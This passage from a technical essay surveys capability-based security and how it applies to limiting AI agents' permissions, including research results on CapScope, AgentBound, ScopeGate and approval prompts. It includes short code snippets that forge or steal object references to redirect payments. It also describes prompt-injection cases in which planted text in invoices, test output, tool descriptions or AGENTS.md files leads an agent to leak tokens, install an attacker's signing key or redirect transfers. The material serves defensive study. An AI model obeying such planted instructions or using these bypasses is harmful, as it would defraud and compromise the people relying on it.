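### Can capabilities be confined or revoked?

Boebert's paper also encouraged the broader claim that capability systems cannot solve the confinement problem. This problem, which Lampson posed in 1973, is how a customer can run somebody else's program on private data and be sure that the program will not leak the data. In 1988, Karger wrote that capability systems had "a fundamental inability" to solve it. Yet in the same work he reported that KeyKOS achieved confinement using a mechanism called a factory.

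With a factory, the program's maker supplies only code, and the customer supplies every reference the program starts with. Miller and Shapiro compare this to buying a pocket calculator from a manufacturer one doesn't trust. The customer can see that no wires come out of it, and so can enter financial figures without worrying that they will get back to the manufacturer. The firm's harness does much the same for the agent's code, since the references it supplies are the program's only connections to the outside. But the program can still use those references, so it could send the accountant everything it finds in the folder.

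Confinement also requires that whatever starts the program does not add any access of its own. The customer must also start the program, rather than send data to a service that is already running. If the firm sent its invoices to a supplier's online service, it could not tell what else that service was connected to.

In a widely cited 1997 paper on Java, Wallach and colleagues objected that two programs that can exchange references can share their capabilities without the system intervening. They concluded that every program holding a capability must be trusted to protect it. That holds for such programs, but the owner may be able to keep programs apart, or connect them only through a diode or membrane. This is easy for a calculator but gets harder as programs need more connections to be useful, and someone has to consider each one.

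The claim about revocation has a similar weakness, because it holds for permission but not for authority. In 2001, Chander, Dean and Mitchell wrote that revocation was "infeasible" in systems based on unforgeable references, although Redell had described the forwarder in 1974. They were right that nobody can take a reference away from a program that holds it. But when the harness turns off a forwarder, the invoice program loses its authority over the folder, even though it keeps its reference to the forwarder.

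Access lists still have the advantage that an administrator can delete an account's entry from a file's list at any time, without preparation. With capabilities, the owner has to hand out a forwarder in advance. If the harness gave the program a direct reference to the folder, the harness could not later replace that reference with one it can switch off. Using forwarders routinely would avoid this problem and need not slow access much. KeyKOS and a later system, EROS, cached where chains of forwarders led, so most uses were still fast.

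### Stating what an object must not be able to cause

The payer, the membrane and the diode are all short, but people who rely on them need to know that their code is correct, and careful reading may not be enough to establish this. *Policy as Types* (Meredith, Stay and Drossopoulou, 2013) cites a review in which security specialists spent 90 person-hours on about a hundred lines of well-commented Python without uncovering three bugs that someone had inserted deliberately.

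A proof could give more assurance, but it needs a precise statement of what to prove. An ordinary specification describes what a method does when called. The payer's specification might require `pay` to transfer the given amount to the supplier's account if the supplier is on the list. A payer could satisfy this specification and still have a second method that pays anyone.

Drossopoulou and Noble argued that capability-based programs need a different kind of specification, which they called deniability policies. Such a policy states a necessary condition for an effect. For instance, code can change the balance of a bank account only if it has access to that account. The policy is also "open", meaning it must remain true whatever code anyone adds to the module. An open policy for the payer would be that no program can make it send money to an account outside the register. The second method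 would violate this policy even if no existing program called it.

Meredith and colleagues express deniability in a small mathematical language for programs that run side by side and exchange messages over channels. A channel serves as a capability. Consider a memory cell that other programs can reach only through a channel called *slot*, and a program *P* that has no access to *slot*. If *slot* is hidden from everything else, then

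*P* running beside the cell ≈ *P* running alone

where ≈ means that no observer could tell the two apart by exchanging messages with them. *P* therefore cannot affect the cell in any way that matters to anyone outside. The condition that *P* has no access to *slot* is a type, in the sense that it describes a class of programs by their behaviour. Unlike an ordinary type checker, however, no algorithm can be sure to finish checking every condition that this logic can express, although checks do finish for a large class of useful ones.

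Koepe surveys other work on proving such properties. In 2010, Murray modelled capability patterns as communicating processes and used an automatic checker to test whether they had the intended properties. Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens found that existing formal definitions of capability safety were too weak for verifying applications, and proposed a stronger one. Swasey and colleagues developed a logic for proving that patterns stay robust when untrusted code uses them.

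Drossopoulou, with Miller and others, also defined permission and authority formally. As Koepe presents the definitions, an object's current permissions cover itself, the objects its fields refer to and, while one of its methods is running, the objects the method's variables refer to. Its authority covers every object whose fields could change as a result of a call to it. This definition of authority includes the invoice program's ability to alter the ledger through a payment object, but it excludes reading. A program that could copy the whole payroll without changing anything would therefore have no authority over it in this sense.

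## What keeps a capability from being forged

The payer protects the firm's money only if the invoice program can neither access the bank connection inside the payer nor create its own. Programming languages, operating systems, processors and cryptography can all enforce this, but they differ in overhead and in what must work correctly for the protection to hold.

### What a language has to rule out

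According to *CallE* (2019), the object-capability model relies on two guarantees from the language: code cannot forge references, and it can perform restricted operations only by calling methods on objects. A language that provides both is called capability-safe.

It must be memory-safe, so that code cannot turn a number into a reference or read memory it has no reference to. C allows both:

```
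Bank *forged = (Bank *) 0x5581a0;   /* an address the program worked out */
Bank *stolen = *(Bank **) payer;    /* the first field inside the payer */
```

It must also have real encapsulation, so that an object can keep a reference to itself. In Python, a leading underscore tells other programmers that a field is private, but nothing stops them from using it:

```
payer._bank.transfer("attacker's account", 9400)
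```

Code must have no global access to resources. Any Java code can try to open any file by name, even if it starts with no references at all:

```
new FileReader("/payroll/2026.csv")
```

Finally, casts and reflection must not recover what an object hides. Reflection lets a program inspect and manipulate its own objects, and in Java it can switch off the protection on a private field:

```
Field f = payer.getClass().getDeclaredField("bank");
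f.setAccessible(true);
Bank stolen = (Bank) f.get(payer);
```

Java has been able to block this between separate modules since 2017, but not within one module. Casts are a subtler problem. If the harness hands out a folder under a type that lists only reading methods, the program can cast it back to the full type and delete files. The harness has to hand out a separate object that can only read.

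### Joe-E, E, Hardened JavaScript and safe Rust

*Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) makes Java capability-safe by removing features. Every Joe-E program is an ordinary Java program that also passes a checker. The checker rejects native methods (code that runs outside Java's rules) and global variables that can change or lead to anything that can. It also limits programs to a "tamed" part of Java's standard library.

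Taming requires attention to small details. A reference to a file should give access to that file only, but Java's `getParentFile()` lets a program reach the root of the disk from any file, so Joe-E leaves it out. `new File(dir, name)` normally opens a file inside `dir`, but if `dir` is null, Java treats `name` as a full path and will open any file on the disk. Joe-E replaces it with a wrapper that checks for null.

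References can also escape through exceptions. Suppose the payer passes its bank connection to a currency converter, which fails and throws an exception with the connection inside. If the payer doesn't catch the exception, it propagates to the invoice program, which can extract the connection. Nothing in the payer's code shows the danger. Joe-E therefore requires exceptions to be immutable, which means they cannot contain capabilities like this one.

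E, the language that Miller and others developed, has its own syntax and leaves out Java's changeable global variables. But its main implementation runs on Java and borrows Java's libraries, so its developers had to tame those libraries too. A security review found that they had mistakenly allowed several unsafe methods. For this reason, Mettler and colleagues call taming a substantial weakness of their own approach. Joe-E also doesn't limit a program's use of memory or processor time, whereas the operating system KeyKOS limited processor time with objects called meters.

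JavaScript is memory-safe, and a function's local variables are properly private. Its weak point is that all code in a program shares the same built-in objects and can change them. If the payer keeps its suppliers' accounts in a `Map`, one line elsewhere can redirect every payment:

```
Map.prototype.get = function (key) { return "attacker's account"; };
```

Hardened JavaScript freezes the built-in objects before other code runs. It then runs each piece of untrusted code in a compartment with its own global variables, which include no network or file access unless somebody adds it. Some older libraries fail because they modify the built-in objects. The cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask uses Hardened JavaScript to run extensions from outside developers.

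Safe Rust excludes `unsafe` blocks, which let programmers do things the compiler can't check. Safe code can calculate an address but can't read or write the memory there. This isn't enough for capability safety, because Rust's standard library can open any file by name. On Linux, a safe program can even open `/proc/self/mem`, a file that represents the program's own memory, and use it to overwrite a private reference. A capability-safe version of Rust also has to remove the library functions that open files by name.

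### Enforcement outside the language

An agent's tools may come from many suppliers and be written in many languages, so the firm may need protection that doesn't depend on how each program is written.

| Mechanism | What prevents forgery | What must work correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Capability-safe language | the language's rules | compiler or checker, runtime, tamed libraries |
| Capability kernel | programs cannot write to the kernel's lists | kernel, processor, devices with direct access to memory |
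| Capsicum | the kernel's table of open files | the whole FreeBSD kernel, processor |
| WebAssembly's system interface | the runtime's table of handles | runtime and its compiler, the functions the host supplies |
| CHERI | a validity bit on each pointer | processor, and the software that creates the first pointers |
| Macaroons and Biscuit | cryptography | secret keys, the checking service, everyone who holds a token |

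KeyKOS and its successor EROS kept capabilities in storage that programs could not write as data. A program used a capability by giving the kernel its position in a list, much as in Dennis and Van Horn's design. Both systems regularly saved their entire state to disk, so programs still held their capabilities after a restart.

Capsicum, which FreeBSD has included by default since 2014, turns Unix file handles into something closer to true capabilities. A program opens the files it needs and then calls `cap_enter()`. After that, the kernel refuses requests to open files by global names, so the program has to work with the handles it holds. Each handle can also carry a list of permitted operations. The `cat` command could copy a file this way without keeping access to everything its user owns. When Capsicum's designers tested a sandboxed version of the compression program gzip in 2010, it ran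 within 5% of the original's time on files of about 512 kilobytes. For small files, starting the sandbox took up a larger share of the running time.

WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that browsers and servers can run in isolation. The cloud company Fastly uses it to run customers' code. A WebAssembly program can affect anything outside itself only through functions its host supplies. With the standard system interface, WASI, the host typically gives the program handles for particular directories, and the program opens files relative to those. The isolation applies to the program as a whole, so a C program compiled to WebAssembly can still corrupt its own memory and use the wrong one of its handles.

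### What the seL4 proofs cover

A bug in a kernel's code can break its protection. seL4, a small capability kernel that uses a variant of the take-grant rules, has the strongest evidence that its code is correct. According to the seL4 project, machine-checked proofs show that its C code behaves exactly as its specification describes. For some processors, further proofs show that the compiled machine code matches the C, and that a program cannot change data or learn information without authorisation.

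The proofs' coverage depends on the processor. seL4's *Verified Configurations* lists the full set of proofs for one 32-bit Arm board but, for the 64-bit Intel-style processors found in most PCs, only the proof about the C code. Proofcraft (2026), a company that works on the proofs, completed the confidentiality proof for 64-bit Arm in August 2026. In June it had verified the C code of a real-time version of seL4 on RISC-V, an open processor design.

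seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* sets out what could still go wrong. The proofs take for granted about 340 lines of assembly code on Arm, about 1,200 lines of start-up code, and the hardware. They also assume that devices which can access memory without going through the processor do not misuse this access. Confidentiality excludes timing channels, though Sison (2026), in *Clearing roadblocks to Time Protection verification for seL4*, described work towards a proof that would cover them.

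The project reports no functional defects in its roughly 10,000 lines of verified code since it completed the first proof in 2009. Since then, developers have found small defects in every kind of unverified code in the kernel, including start-up code, and in multicore versions. This suggests that the proofs have helped, since the same team wrote and tested both kinds of code. But the proofs don't show that anyone has distributed the capabilities sensibly. If the firm gives two programs write access to each other, the kernel will allow them to interfere.

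### Replacing hardware separation with language safety

On a Raspberry Pi 3B+, using one capability-protected object in seL4 takes 379 processor cycles, including 139 to switch between the program and the kernel. Xu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *safeL4*, tried to avoid this overhead with a Rust kernel that shares one address space with its file system and device drivers. The Rust compiler isolates these components from one another, so a request from one to another is an ordinary function call.

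In Rust, an owner cannot take back a standard shared pointer, and the object stays alive for as long as anyone holds one. safeL4 therefore gives components a weak pointer, which does not keep the object alive, inside a structure they can't open. For each call, the kernel checks the holder's rights and turns the weak pointer into a usable one until the call ends. The kernel also records which capability came from which, so an owner can revoke a capability and everything derived from it without setting up a forwarder in advance.

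safeL4 was on average 1.91 times as fast as seL4 across seL4's own speed tests. Calling another component took 32 cycles instead of 249, but creating a capability for a block of memory took 949 instead of 538, mainly because safeL4 gives each object its own lock. The advantage shrank to 14.3% with the database SQLite, which is written in C and so still had to run behind hardware separation.

safeL4 achieves this speed by relying on more software. Its protection depends on the Rust compiler, Rust's core libraries and 1,765 lines of unsafe code in the kernel, and it has no proof like seL4's. On some processors, the seL4 proofs remove even the need to trust the compiler. The difference matters because compilers have bugs: in 2024, a project called cve-rs used one in the Rust compiler to corrupt memory without any `unsafe` blocks.

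A safe language alone also doesn't prevent confused deputies. Xu and colleagues point to RedLeaf, another operating system written in Rust, where a driver could ask a central service for access to a device by giving the device's identification numbers. A driver could get access to a different device by giving that device's numbers. In safeL4, a driver instead receives a capability for its own device when it starts.

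### Capabilities in the processor

CHERI, a set of processor extensions, makes pointers unforgeable, even in C. It replaces each 64-bit pointer with a 128-bit one that contains an address, the limits of the memory it may reach, and permissions. A separate bit marks the pointer as valid. If a program overwrites any part of the pointer with ordinary data, the processor clears this bit and the pointer stops working. Programs can make new pointers only from ones they have, by narrowing the limits or permissions.

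This would stop the first line of the C attack on the payer, which makes a pointer from a number. It might not stop the second line, which reads the payer's contents through a valid pointer the program already has. To hide the bank connection, the firm would have to "seal" that pointer, so that the program could pass it around but not read what it points to.

Published slowdown figures vary widely. In *Early performance results from the prototype Morello microarchitecture*, Watson, Clarke and colleagues (2023) measured an average slowdown of 15.17% on Morello, Arm's prototype design. They used a compilation mode that gave less protection but avoided a weakness in how the prototype predicts jumps. Without that mode, the slowdown was 28.01%, according to an earlier version of the report, CTSRD-CHERI's *Initial results*. Two improvements to the design reduced the slowdown in the reduced-protection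 mode to 6.28%. Watson and colleagues estimate 2.2% to 3.2% for a future processor, based on ordinary code with its pointers widened to match CHERI's.

*Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* (Meignan--Masson, Fink and colleagues, 2026) reports slowdowns of 20% to 60% for databases on Morello. Databases follow many pointers, and doubling a pointer's size halves the number that fit in the processor's fast memory. These figures are a better guide to the hardware people can test now, since the 2.2% to 3.2% estimate has not yet been confirmed on a chip.

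Systems that use CHERI must also find or disable pointers to freed memory. Otherwise, such a pointer stays valid and may later reach whatever another part of the program stores there. *CHERI-D* (2026) reports an average overhead of 1.6% for a new method on one set of benchmarks, against 5.8% and 13.3% for two earlier ones. On SQLite, however, the new method's overhead was about 6%, nearly the same as that of the method that had averaged 13.3% on the benchmarks.

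CHERI has begun to move beyond prototypes in small devices. In CHERIoT's *ICENI on a development board* (2026), a co-founder of SCI Semiconductor announced that the company had made the first chip to implement a version of CHERI for microcontrollers. The chip runs at up to 250 MHz, which suits a sensor or a controller but not a database server. The company raised £5 million in September to scale up production, according to Today's Startup News' *SCI Semiconductor Raises £5M* (2026). *CHERI Mocha* (Orensanz Martinez, 2026) reports that CHERI adds 57% to the circuit area of a very small processor core. Ordinary memory protection adds 42% to the same core, so the core with CHERI is about 11% larger than the core with ordinary protection.

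### Tokens that travel between machines

A kernel or compiler can't control a reference once a program sends it to another company's computer. The sender has to turn the reference into data, called a token, and the receiving service needs a way to tell real tokens from forged ones.

Macaroons, which Google researchers introduced in 2014, do this with a keyed hash, a short code that only someone with the right key can calculate. The service picks a secret key *K* and gives the token an identifier. The token's first code is

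*s*₀ = HMAC(*K*, identifier).

Anyone who holds the token can add a restriction *c*, such as "only supplier 17" or "expires on 30 June". They replace the old code with a new one that uses the old code as its key:

*s*₁ = HMAC(*s*₀, *c*).

The service repeats the calculation from *K* and checks that the codes match and the restrictions hold. A holder who receives only *s*₁ cannot remove the restriction, because that would require recovering *s*₀ from *s*₁. The firm can therefore weaken a token without contacting the bank. PyPI, the main public collection of Python packages, uses macaroons as upload credentials.

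Only a service that has the secret key *K* can check a macaroon. Biscuit, a newer design, uses public-key signatures instead, so any service with the public key can check a token without being able to issue one. Biscuit expresses restrictions as small logic programs.

Anyone with a copy of either kind of token can use it, unless the service also checks the holder's identity. If the harness puts a payment token in the text that a model reads, a hidden line in an invoice could cause the model to email the token to the supplier. The harness should keep tokens out of the model's text and attach them to tool calls after the model has written the calls.

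### Why so few mainstream systems use them

Sixty years after Dennis and Van Horn's design, most programs still start with all their user's powers, so it is reasonable to ask whether capabilities are impractical. Designers once expected the small kernels that use capabilities to become the basis of all operating systems, but they have remained mainly in embedded and safety-critical devices. Xu and colleagues attribute this to the kernels' slow speed. Miller and colleagues instead emphasise mistaken beliefs about capabilities, such as the one that grew out of Boebert's paper.

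Speed cannot be the whole explanation, because Joe-E did not become widely used either, even though its checker doesn't alter the programs it accepts and they run as ordinary Java. Mettler and colleagues expected most existing Java code to fail the checker, and found that programmers need training in designing with capabilities. Koepe notes that Java is capability-safe only if the whole program follows the restrictions. A company therefore has to do much of the work before it gets the full benefit, and every old library it wants to keep adds to that work.

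This would explain why capability systems do best where one organisation controls most of the software. The Chinese carmaker NIO uses an seL4-based system in its ONVO L60 car. More than 600,000 NIO vehicles run systems from its SkyOS family, but some of those systems are based on other software, such as Android. Huawei's HongMeng kernel also uses capabilities, but Xu and colleagues report that it keeps its most critical services inside the kernel for speed, which reduces separation.

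These rules may be easier to apply to programs that agents write, because there is no old code to convert. The firm's agent writes a new program each month, and the harness can require a restricted language, as Scala's safe mode does. Somebody still has to tame the libraries that the program calls.

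## Choosing what to grant

Even a verified kernel such as seL4 enforces a careless grant as strictly as a careful one. Someone has to decide what the invoice program should get, which *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) calls the policy specification problem and describes as unsolved. The firm could make the decision in four ways:

| Method | Who decides | When | Example from the invoice task |
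|---|---|---|---|
| User's own choice | the bookkeeper | while setting the task | she selects the invoice folder, and the selection grants access to it |
| Manifest | the tool's maker | before anyone uses the tool | the mail tool declares that it needs the network |
| Prediction | a language model | after the request, before the work | the model lists the folder, the payment tool and the accountant's address |
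| Approval prompt | the bookkeeper | at each action | she approves or refuses each payment |

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) surveyed 21 proposals for letting users control an agent's permissions. They looked for three qualities: little work for the user, rules with a formal definition, and enforcement that does not depend on an AI model's judgement. No proposal fully achieved all three. The five commercial agents they tested tended either to interrupt the user often or to leave decisions to an AI reviewer that users could barely inspect or control.

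### Granting by choosing

Suppose Alice's text editor starts with no access to her files. When she clicks "Open", the operating system shows her a file picker. She selects a file, and the system gives the editor a reference to it. Sandboxed Mac apps open files this way. Alice doesn't have to answer a separate permission prompt, because choosing the file, which she had to do anyway, also grants access. Similarly, when a user types `cat < foo.txt`, their choice of file determines which handle `cat` receives.

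The bookkeeper could choose the invoice folder and the accountant's address this way. She can't choose the payees and amounts without reading the invoices, which is the work she wanted to hand over. *Trident* (2026) addresses a similar case where the payee's name appears only inside an email. Before the agent reads the email, a language model selects a template that permits, for example, one payment to a vendor already on file, and the details come later. The model may lower the template's limit to an amount the user mentioned, but it can't write or widen a template. The email can then affect which listed vendor gets paid but can't add a vendor to the list.

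### Why people stop reading approval prompts

Agents that ask before each risky action run into approval fatigue, which Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* defines as people no longer paying close attention to what they approve. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans the agent proposes, so they do not simply agree to everything. Nearly half of active command-line users had also written rules that allow certain shell commands without a prompt, and many of these rules were broad enough to let the agent run any code.

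A high approval rate could just mean that most requests are harmless. To test this, Anthropic had a research firm pay 1,053 professional testers to work with the agent, and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

Anthropic published these results to justify replacing most prompts with an automated check, which blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful than someone protecting real files. But that was also true at the start of a session, so it doesn't explain why they became less careful later.

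Asking people to set rules in advance may not help. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise an assistant through a simulated day. Seven of the assistant's 18 actions, such as reading private messages or buying airport lounge access, went beyond what the user had requested. People who approved or blocked every action themselves blocked 60% of these. People who saw only the actions that an AI reviewer passed on to them blocked 54%. People who first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action blocked only about 40%.

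The third group chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which put most decisions off until the assistant was working. They then approved two thirds of the excessive actions they were asked about. Yan added people to this group after the initial random assignment, so the comparison is weaker than a fully randomised one.

Even so, the people who approved every action in Yan's study did much better than Anthropic's testers. Yan's participants saw only 18 prompts, each describing its action in plain language. Shell commands are harder to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative (some reports involved both). For instance, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving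 it permits whatever code the script contains.

Users who turn on automatic approval may still be watching their agents. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites usage data in which experienced users turned it on more often but also interrupted their agents more often. Repeated approvals, however, are poor evidence of what a user wants. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 for *Let the Agent Do It?*, and advised toolmakers not to treat repeated approvals as a stable preference. If the bookkeeper approves 39 payments in a row, the harness should not treat that as approval of the fortieth.

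### Manifests for tool servers

A manifest lists the kinds of access a piece of software needs. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) adapts Android's permission list for servers that use the Model Context Protocol, the most widely used standard for connecting agents to tools. These servers often run with all the permissions of the user who started them.

AgentBound's manifests use a fixed vocabulary, with entries such as "read files" and "connect to the network". A language model reads the server's code and documentation and writes five drafts of the manifest, and a second model merges them. When the server runs, the user narrows each entry to particular folders or web addresses. The server runs in a container, an isolated environment that blocks all other access. Running in the container added an average of 0.6 milliseconds or less to each operation.

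The manifests' reported accuracy of 80.9% is based on few replies. The researchers sent manifests to the developers of 96 popular servers, and about three quarters did not respond. Of the 21 who gave a verdict, 17 accepted the manifest unchanged. The researchers also wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, and the generated ones matched them on 96.5% of 816 yes-or-no entries. This figure overstates how reliable the manifests are, because a typical server needs only a few of the 17 kinds of access, so many entries are easy to get right. Twenty of the 48 generated manifests contained at least one mistake.

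Most of the mistakes, 23 out of 29, left out access that the researchers had included. These mistakes are less dangerous than granting too much access, because a server that lacks access it needs will fail and somebody will notice, whereas unnecessary access causes no visible problem until an attacker uses it.

In one test, a malicious map server secretly replaced the address of Google's map service with an attacker's. The container blocked the connection because the user had approved only Google's address. In another, the description of a server that was supposed to tell the time included instructions for the agent to redirect cryptocurrency transfers. AgentBound did not stop this attack, because the transfer would go through a service the agent was allowed to use. The invoice agent has the same problem. A manifest can restrict its payment tool to the bank's address, but a payment to the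 dishonest supplier also goes through the bank.

### Predicting what a task needs

Unlike a toolmaker, a language model can read the user's request before proposing a grant. *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?* introduced AuthBench to test this ability. For each of 120 tasks, a model must state which files an agent should be able to read, write or run. People have checked the reference answers. According to the summary of the results in *Trust Is Not a Score* (2026), leading models left out permissions the tasks required and also granted ones that were unused or sensitive. Telling a model to be more cautious would therefore not fix the problem, because the model would probably leave out more of the permissions a task needs.

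Training can make an agent use less of the access it has. Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, trained a small model on 1,500 tasks to stay within the access each task required. On 500 other tasks, the share of attempts it completed safely rose from 64% to 98%. They regard this training as a supplement to permission checks and sandboxes, not a substitute.

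Another option is to test whether a permission is necessary. *Aletheia* (2026) does this for the instruction files that coding agents read, which an attacker could use to request excessive access. It removes one permission at a time and runs the task again. If the result still passes its tests, the task did not need that permission. The method requires tasks that are safe to repeat and can be checked automatically, so it would not suit the invoice agent unless the firm had a realistic simulation of its bank.

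### CapScope's three rules

In *Authority Is Not a String*, Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026) also use a model's prediction, but they obtain it before the agent has read any file contents an attacker could have written. Their system, CapScope, is part of a coding agent's harness. An orchestrator model plans the work and delegates parts of it to sub-agents, each with its own permissions.

CapScope defines a capability as a pair

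Cap[*e*, *φ*],

where *e* is a type of effect (read, write or execute) and *φ* is a test that returns true or false for the arguments of a tool call. It covers a call if the tool has effect *e* and the arguments pass the test. For files, the test checks whether the path lies inside a certain folder, after resolving any shortcuts in the path. For commands, it splits a compound command into its parts and checks each one, so permission to run `pytest`, a program that runs tests, does not extend to a second command attached to it.

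These capabilities are records that the harness keeps outside the model's text. Three rules govern them:

- Mint creates them. A model reads the user's request and the names of the project's files, but not their contents, and predicts what the whole task will need. Ordinary code checks the prediction and turns it into a ceiling, which stays fixed for the session unless the user approves an addition.
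- Derive narrows them for a sub-agent. The orchestrator requests a set of capabilities, and the harness keeps only those that fit within the ceiling. Cap[*e*, *φ*′] fits within Cap[*e*, *φ*] if every argument that passes *φ*′ also passes *φ*.
- Invoke checks each call. The harness carries out a call only if a capability belonging to the sub-agent that made it covers the call.

Suppose a developer asks the agent to fix failing tests in a login system. The ceiling allows reading the project, writing to the source folder `src/`, and running two checking programs. The orchestrator delegates the tests to a sub-agent, the runner, which needs only to read the test files and run `pytest`. A second sub-agent, the patcher, will edit the source.

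An attacker has altered a test file so that the test output includes an official-looking notice that the system's signing key has changed, with instructions to put the new key in `src/auth/keys.py`. The new key belongs to the attacker, who could use it to forge logins. The runner reads the notice and tries to write the key. Derive gave the runner no capability with the effect "write", so Invoke rejects the call.

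A list of forbidden actions would probably not help here, because repairs normally involve editing source files. A single policy for the whole task would not help either, because it would have to let the patcher write to `src/`, and the runner would get the same permission.

### Results from 300 runs

Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They planted instructions in five places: a README, an instruction file called AGENTS.md, a skill file (a reusable set of instructions), a source comment and the test output. They ran every combination three times under four conditions, with the same model and the same division of work among sub-agents.

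| Condition | Attacks executed, out of 75 | Repairs completed, out of 75 | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ambient authority | 47 | 72 | 145 s |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 | 70 | 140 s |
| One policy for the task, shared by all sub-agents | 33 | 68 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 | 68 | 316 s |

The forbidden-action list made almost no difference because the planted instructions asked for ordinary operations, such as running one of the project's own utilities. The fall from 33 to 3 is the best evidence for separate permissions, since both conditions set their limits before the agent read any planted text. The model attempted the planted action in 34 of the 75 CapScope runs, so it was not resisting the attacks.

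CapScope's mean time was more than twice that of the unrestricted agent, partly because the model often kept trying after a refusal. In 27 of those 34 runs, it attempted the planted action more than once. Five runs reached the 15-minute time limit, which raised the mean above the median of 208 seconds.

A ceiling that was too narrow caused only two of the seven failed repairs, because the prediction had left out permission to write to the source. In two others, the runner found the correct fix, but it never reached the patcher. The last three had passing tests but ran out of time.

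All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, which the orchestrator normally reads first. An orchestrator without write permission may still be able to create a sub-agent that has it, which gives the orchestrator authority over the source in the sense used earlier. Bouras and colleagues explain that planted text can affect which capabilities the orchestrator requests within the ceiling. An attack can also succeed if a sub-agent's grant is too wide, for example if it covers a folder when the sub-agent needs only one file.

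The experiment used one model, Qwen3.5-flash, and provides little evidence about large projects, where predicting the necessary permissions would be harder. A model with better training against injection would probably attempt fewer of the planted actions, which would reduce the advantage. The researchers also did not test instructions hidden in file names, which the predicting model reads. And `pytest` runs the project's own code, so an attacker who can change that code may not need to influence the model, and a sandbox has to guard against that attack.

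Bouras and colleagues describe CapScope as a reference monitor (a checkpoint that examines every request), not an object-capability system. The model still refers to files and commands by text. In effect, CapScope stores an access matrix by rows, one for each sub-agent. If the patcher's row covers both the file with the bug and the file with the signing key, a planted comment could still direct the patcher to the key file, just as a user directed Tymshare's compiler to the billing file.

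### Hiding risky tools until the agent needs them

The harness could also change which tools the model can see as the work proceeds. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Babu, 2026) gives each tool a risk score: 0 for reading, 1 for changes that are easy to undo, and 4 for actions such as deleting, sending or paying. Tools with a score above 0 also have conditions. The payment tool, for instance, stays hidden until a trusted step has recorded that someone confirmed the payment.

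At each step, the system looks for the route to the goal with the lowest score,

number of steps + *λ* × total risk,

and shows the model only the tools for the next step whose conditions hold. The operator sets *λ*, the weight given to risk. Suppose that one deletion would reach the goal, but so would four harmless steps. The deletion scores 1 + 4*λ* and the longer route scores 4, so the system prefers the longer route only if *λ* is above 0.75.

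A low *λ* does not make the system more permissive and can cause tasks to fail. In Iyer and Babu's tests with *λ* at 0.5, half of the tasks that required authorisation failed because the system picked risky shortcuts, then kept the tools for them hidden when their conditions did not hold. With *λ* at 2, every task succeeded.

The first test of the method used a simple program that obeyed any planted instruction if it could see the necessary tool. When it could see all 100 tools, every attack succeeded. A filter that considered relevance to the next step but ignored risk reduced the success rate to 25%, and the risk-based limits reduced it to zero. Tests with seven language models produced the same rates for the filter and the limits.

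These figures mostly reflect how the benchmark works. An agent can't call a tool that the harness has removed, so a rate of zero is expected if the harness enforces the list. The 25% matches the share of stress tasks, 20 out of 80, in which Iyer and Babu included a dangerous shortcut. Attacks again succeeded 25% of the time when the planted text could forge the record of a confirmation. This result is more informative because it shows that the protection depends on keeping those records out of an attacker's reach. The method also doesn't check arguments, so once the payment tool is available, a hidden line in an invoice can still affect the account number and the amount.

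### Checking the values in each call

Popular software for building agents has the same gap. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examined the public code of LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and a toolkit from the payment company Stripe. All of them let developers choose which tools an agent can call, but by default none checks whether the values in a call are authorised before carrying it out. In a demonstration with a simulated payment service, LangChain accepted a call that changed a merchant's payout account to an attacker's, because it checked only the format of the account number.

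Developers can add such checks themselves, and Stripe may have others on its own servers, which the audit did not cover. But a developer who assumes that choosing the tools is enough will let the model choose the values. This is particularly risky with cheaper models. In a related test of 27 models, those designed for low cost attempted unauthorised calls 60% of the time on average, compared with 19% for the most capable.

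Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, checks each call against rules the operator wrote. The tool must be on a list, and restricted arguments, such as account numbers, must have approved values. A payment must be an ordinary number between zero and a ceiling. Some calls also need a key that identifies the request, so the service can detect a repeat. ScopeGate refuses any call that fails a check or causes an error.

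It refused all 48 prepared attacks and all 29 unauthorised calls from a model that could learn from earlier refusals. In a separate test, it allowed all ten legitimate calls. The same person designed the checks and the attacks, so other attackers might find weaknesses that these tests missed. An earlier version wrongly accepted "NaN" ("not a number") as a payment amount, because checking whether NaN exceeds the payment ceiling always returns false.

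ScopeGate and CapScope differ over whether a model may help write the rules. Mellafe Zuvic holds that no part of a policy should come from a model's output, even indirectly, because an attacker who can corrupt a call might also corrupt the rule that checks it. CapScope accepts a model's prediction because the model has read only trusted text. The stricter position avoids attacks through file names, but the operator must write every rule. This is feasible when the rules list suppliers' accounts that the firm already keeps on record, but much less feasible when they must list the files that each new programming task will need.

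ScopeGate would stop a payment to an account that is not on the firm's books, but a false amount is harder to catch. If the largest legitimate bill is €10,000, the ceiling has to be at least that high, and a demand for €9,400 instead of €940 will pass. The ceiling also applies to each call separately, so it does not limit the agent's total payments.

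## Recording capabilities in types

CapScope and ScopeGate both check a tool call when the agent makes it. If the invoice program pays 30 suppliers and then attempts a call it has no capability for, the harness refuses it, but the 30 payments have already gone out. Run-time capabilities stop a program from exceeding its access, but they don't show beforehand which of its capabilities a given function will use.

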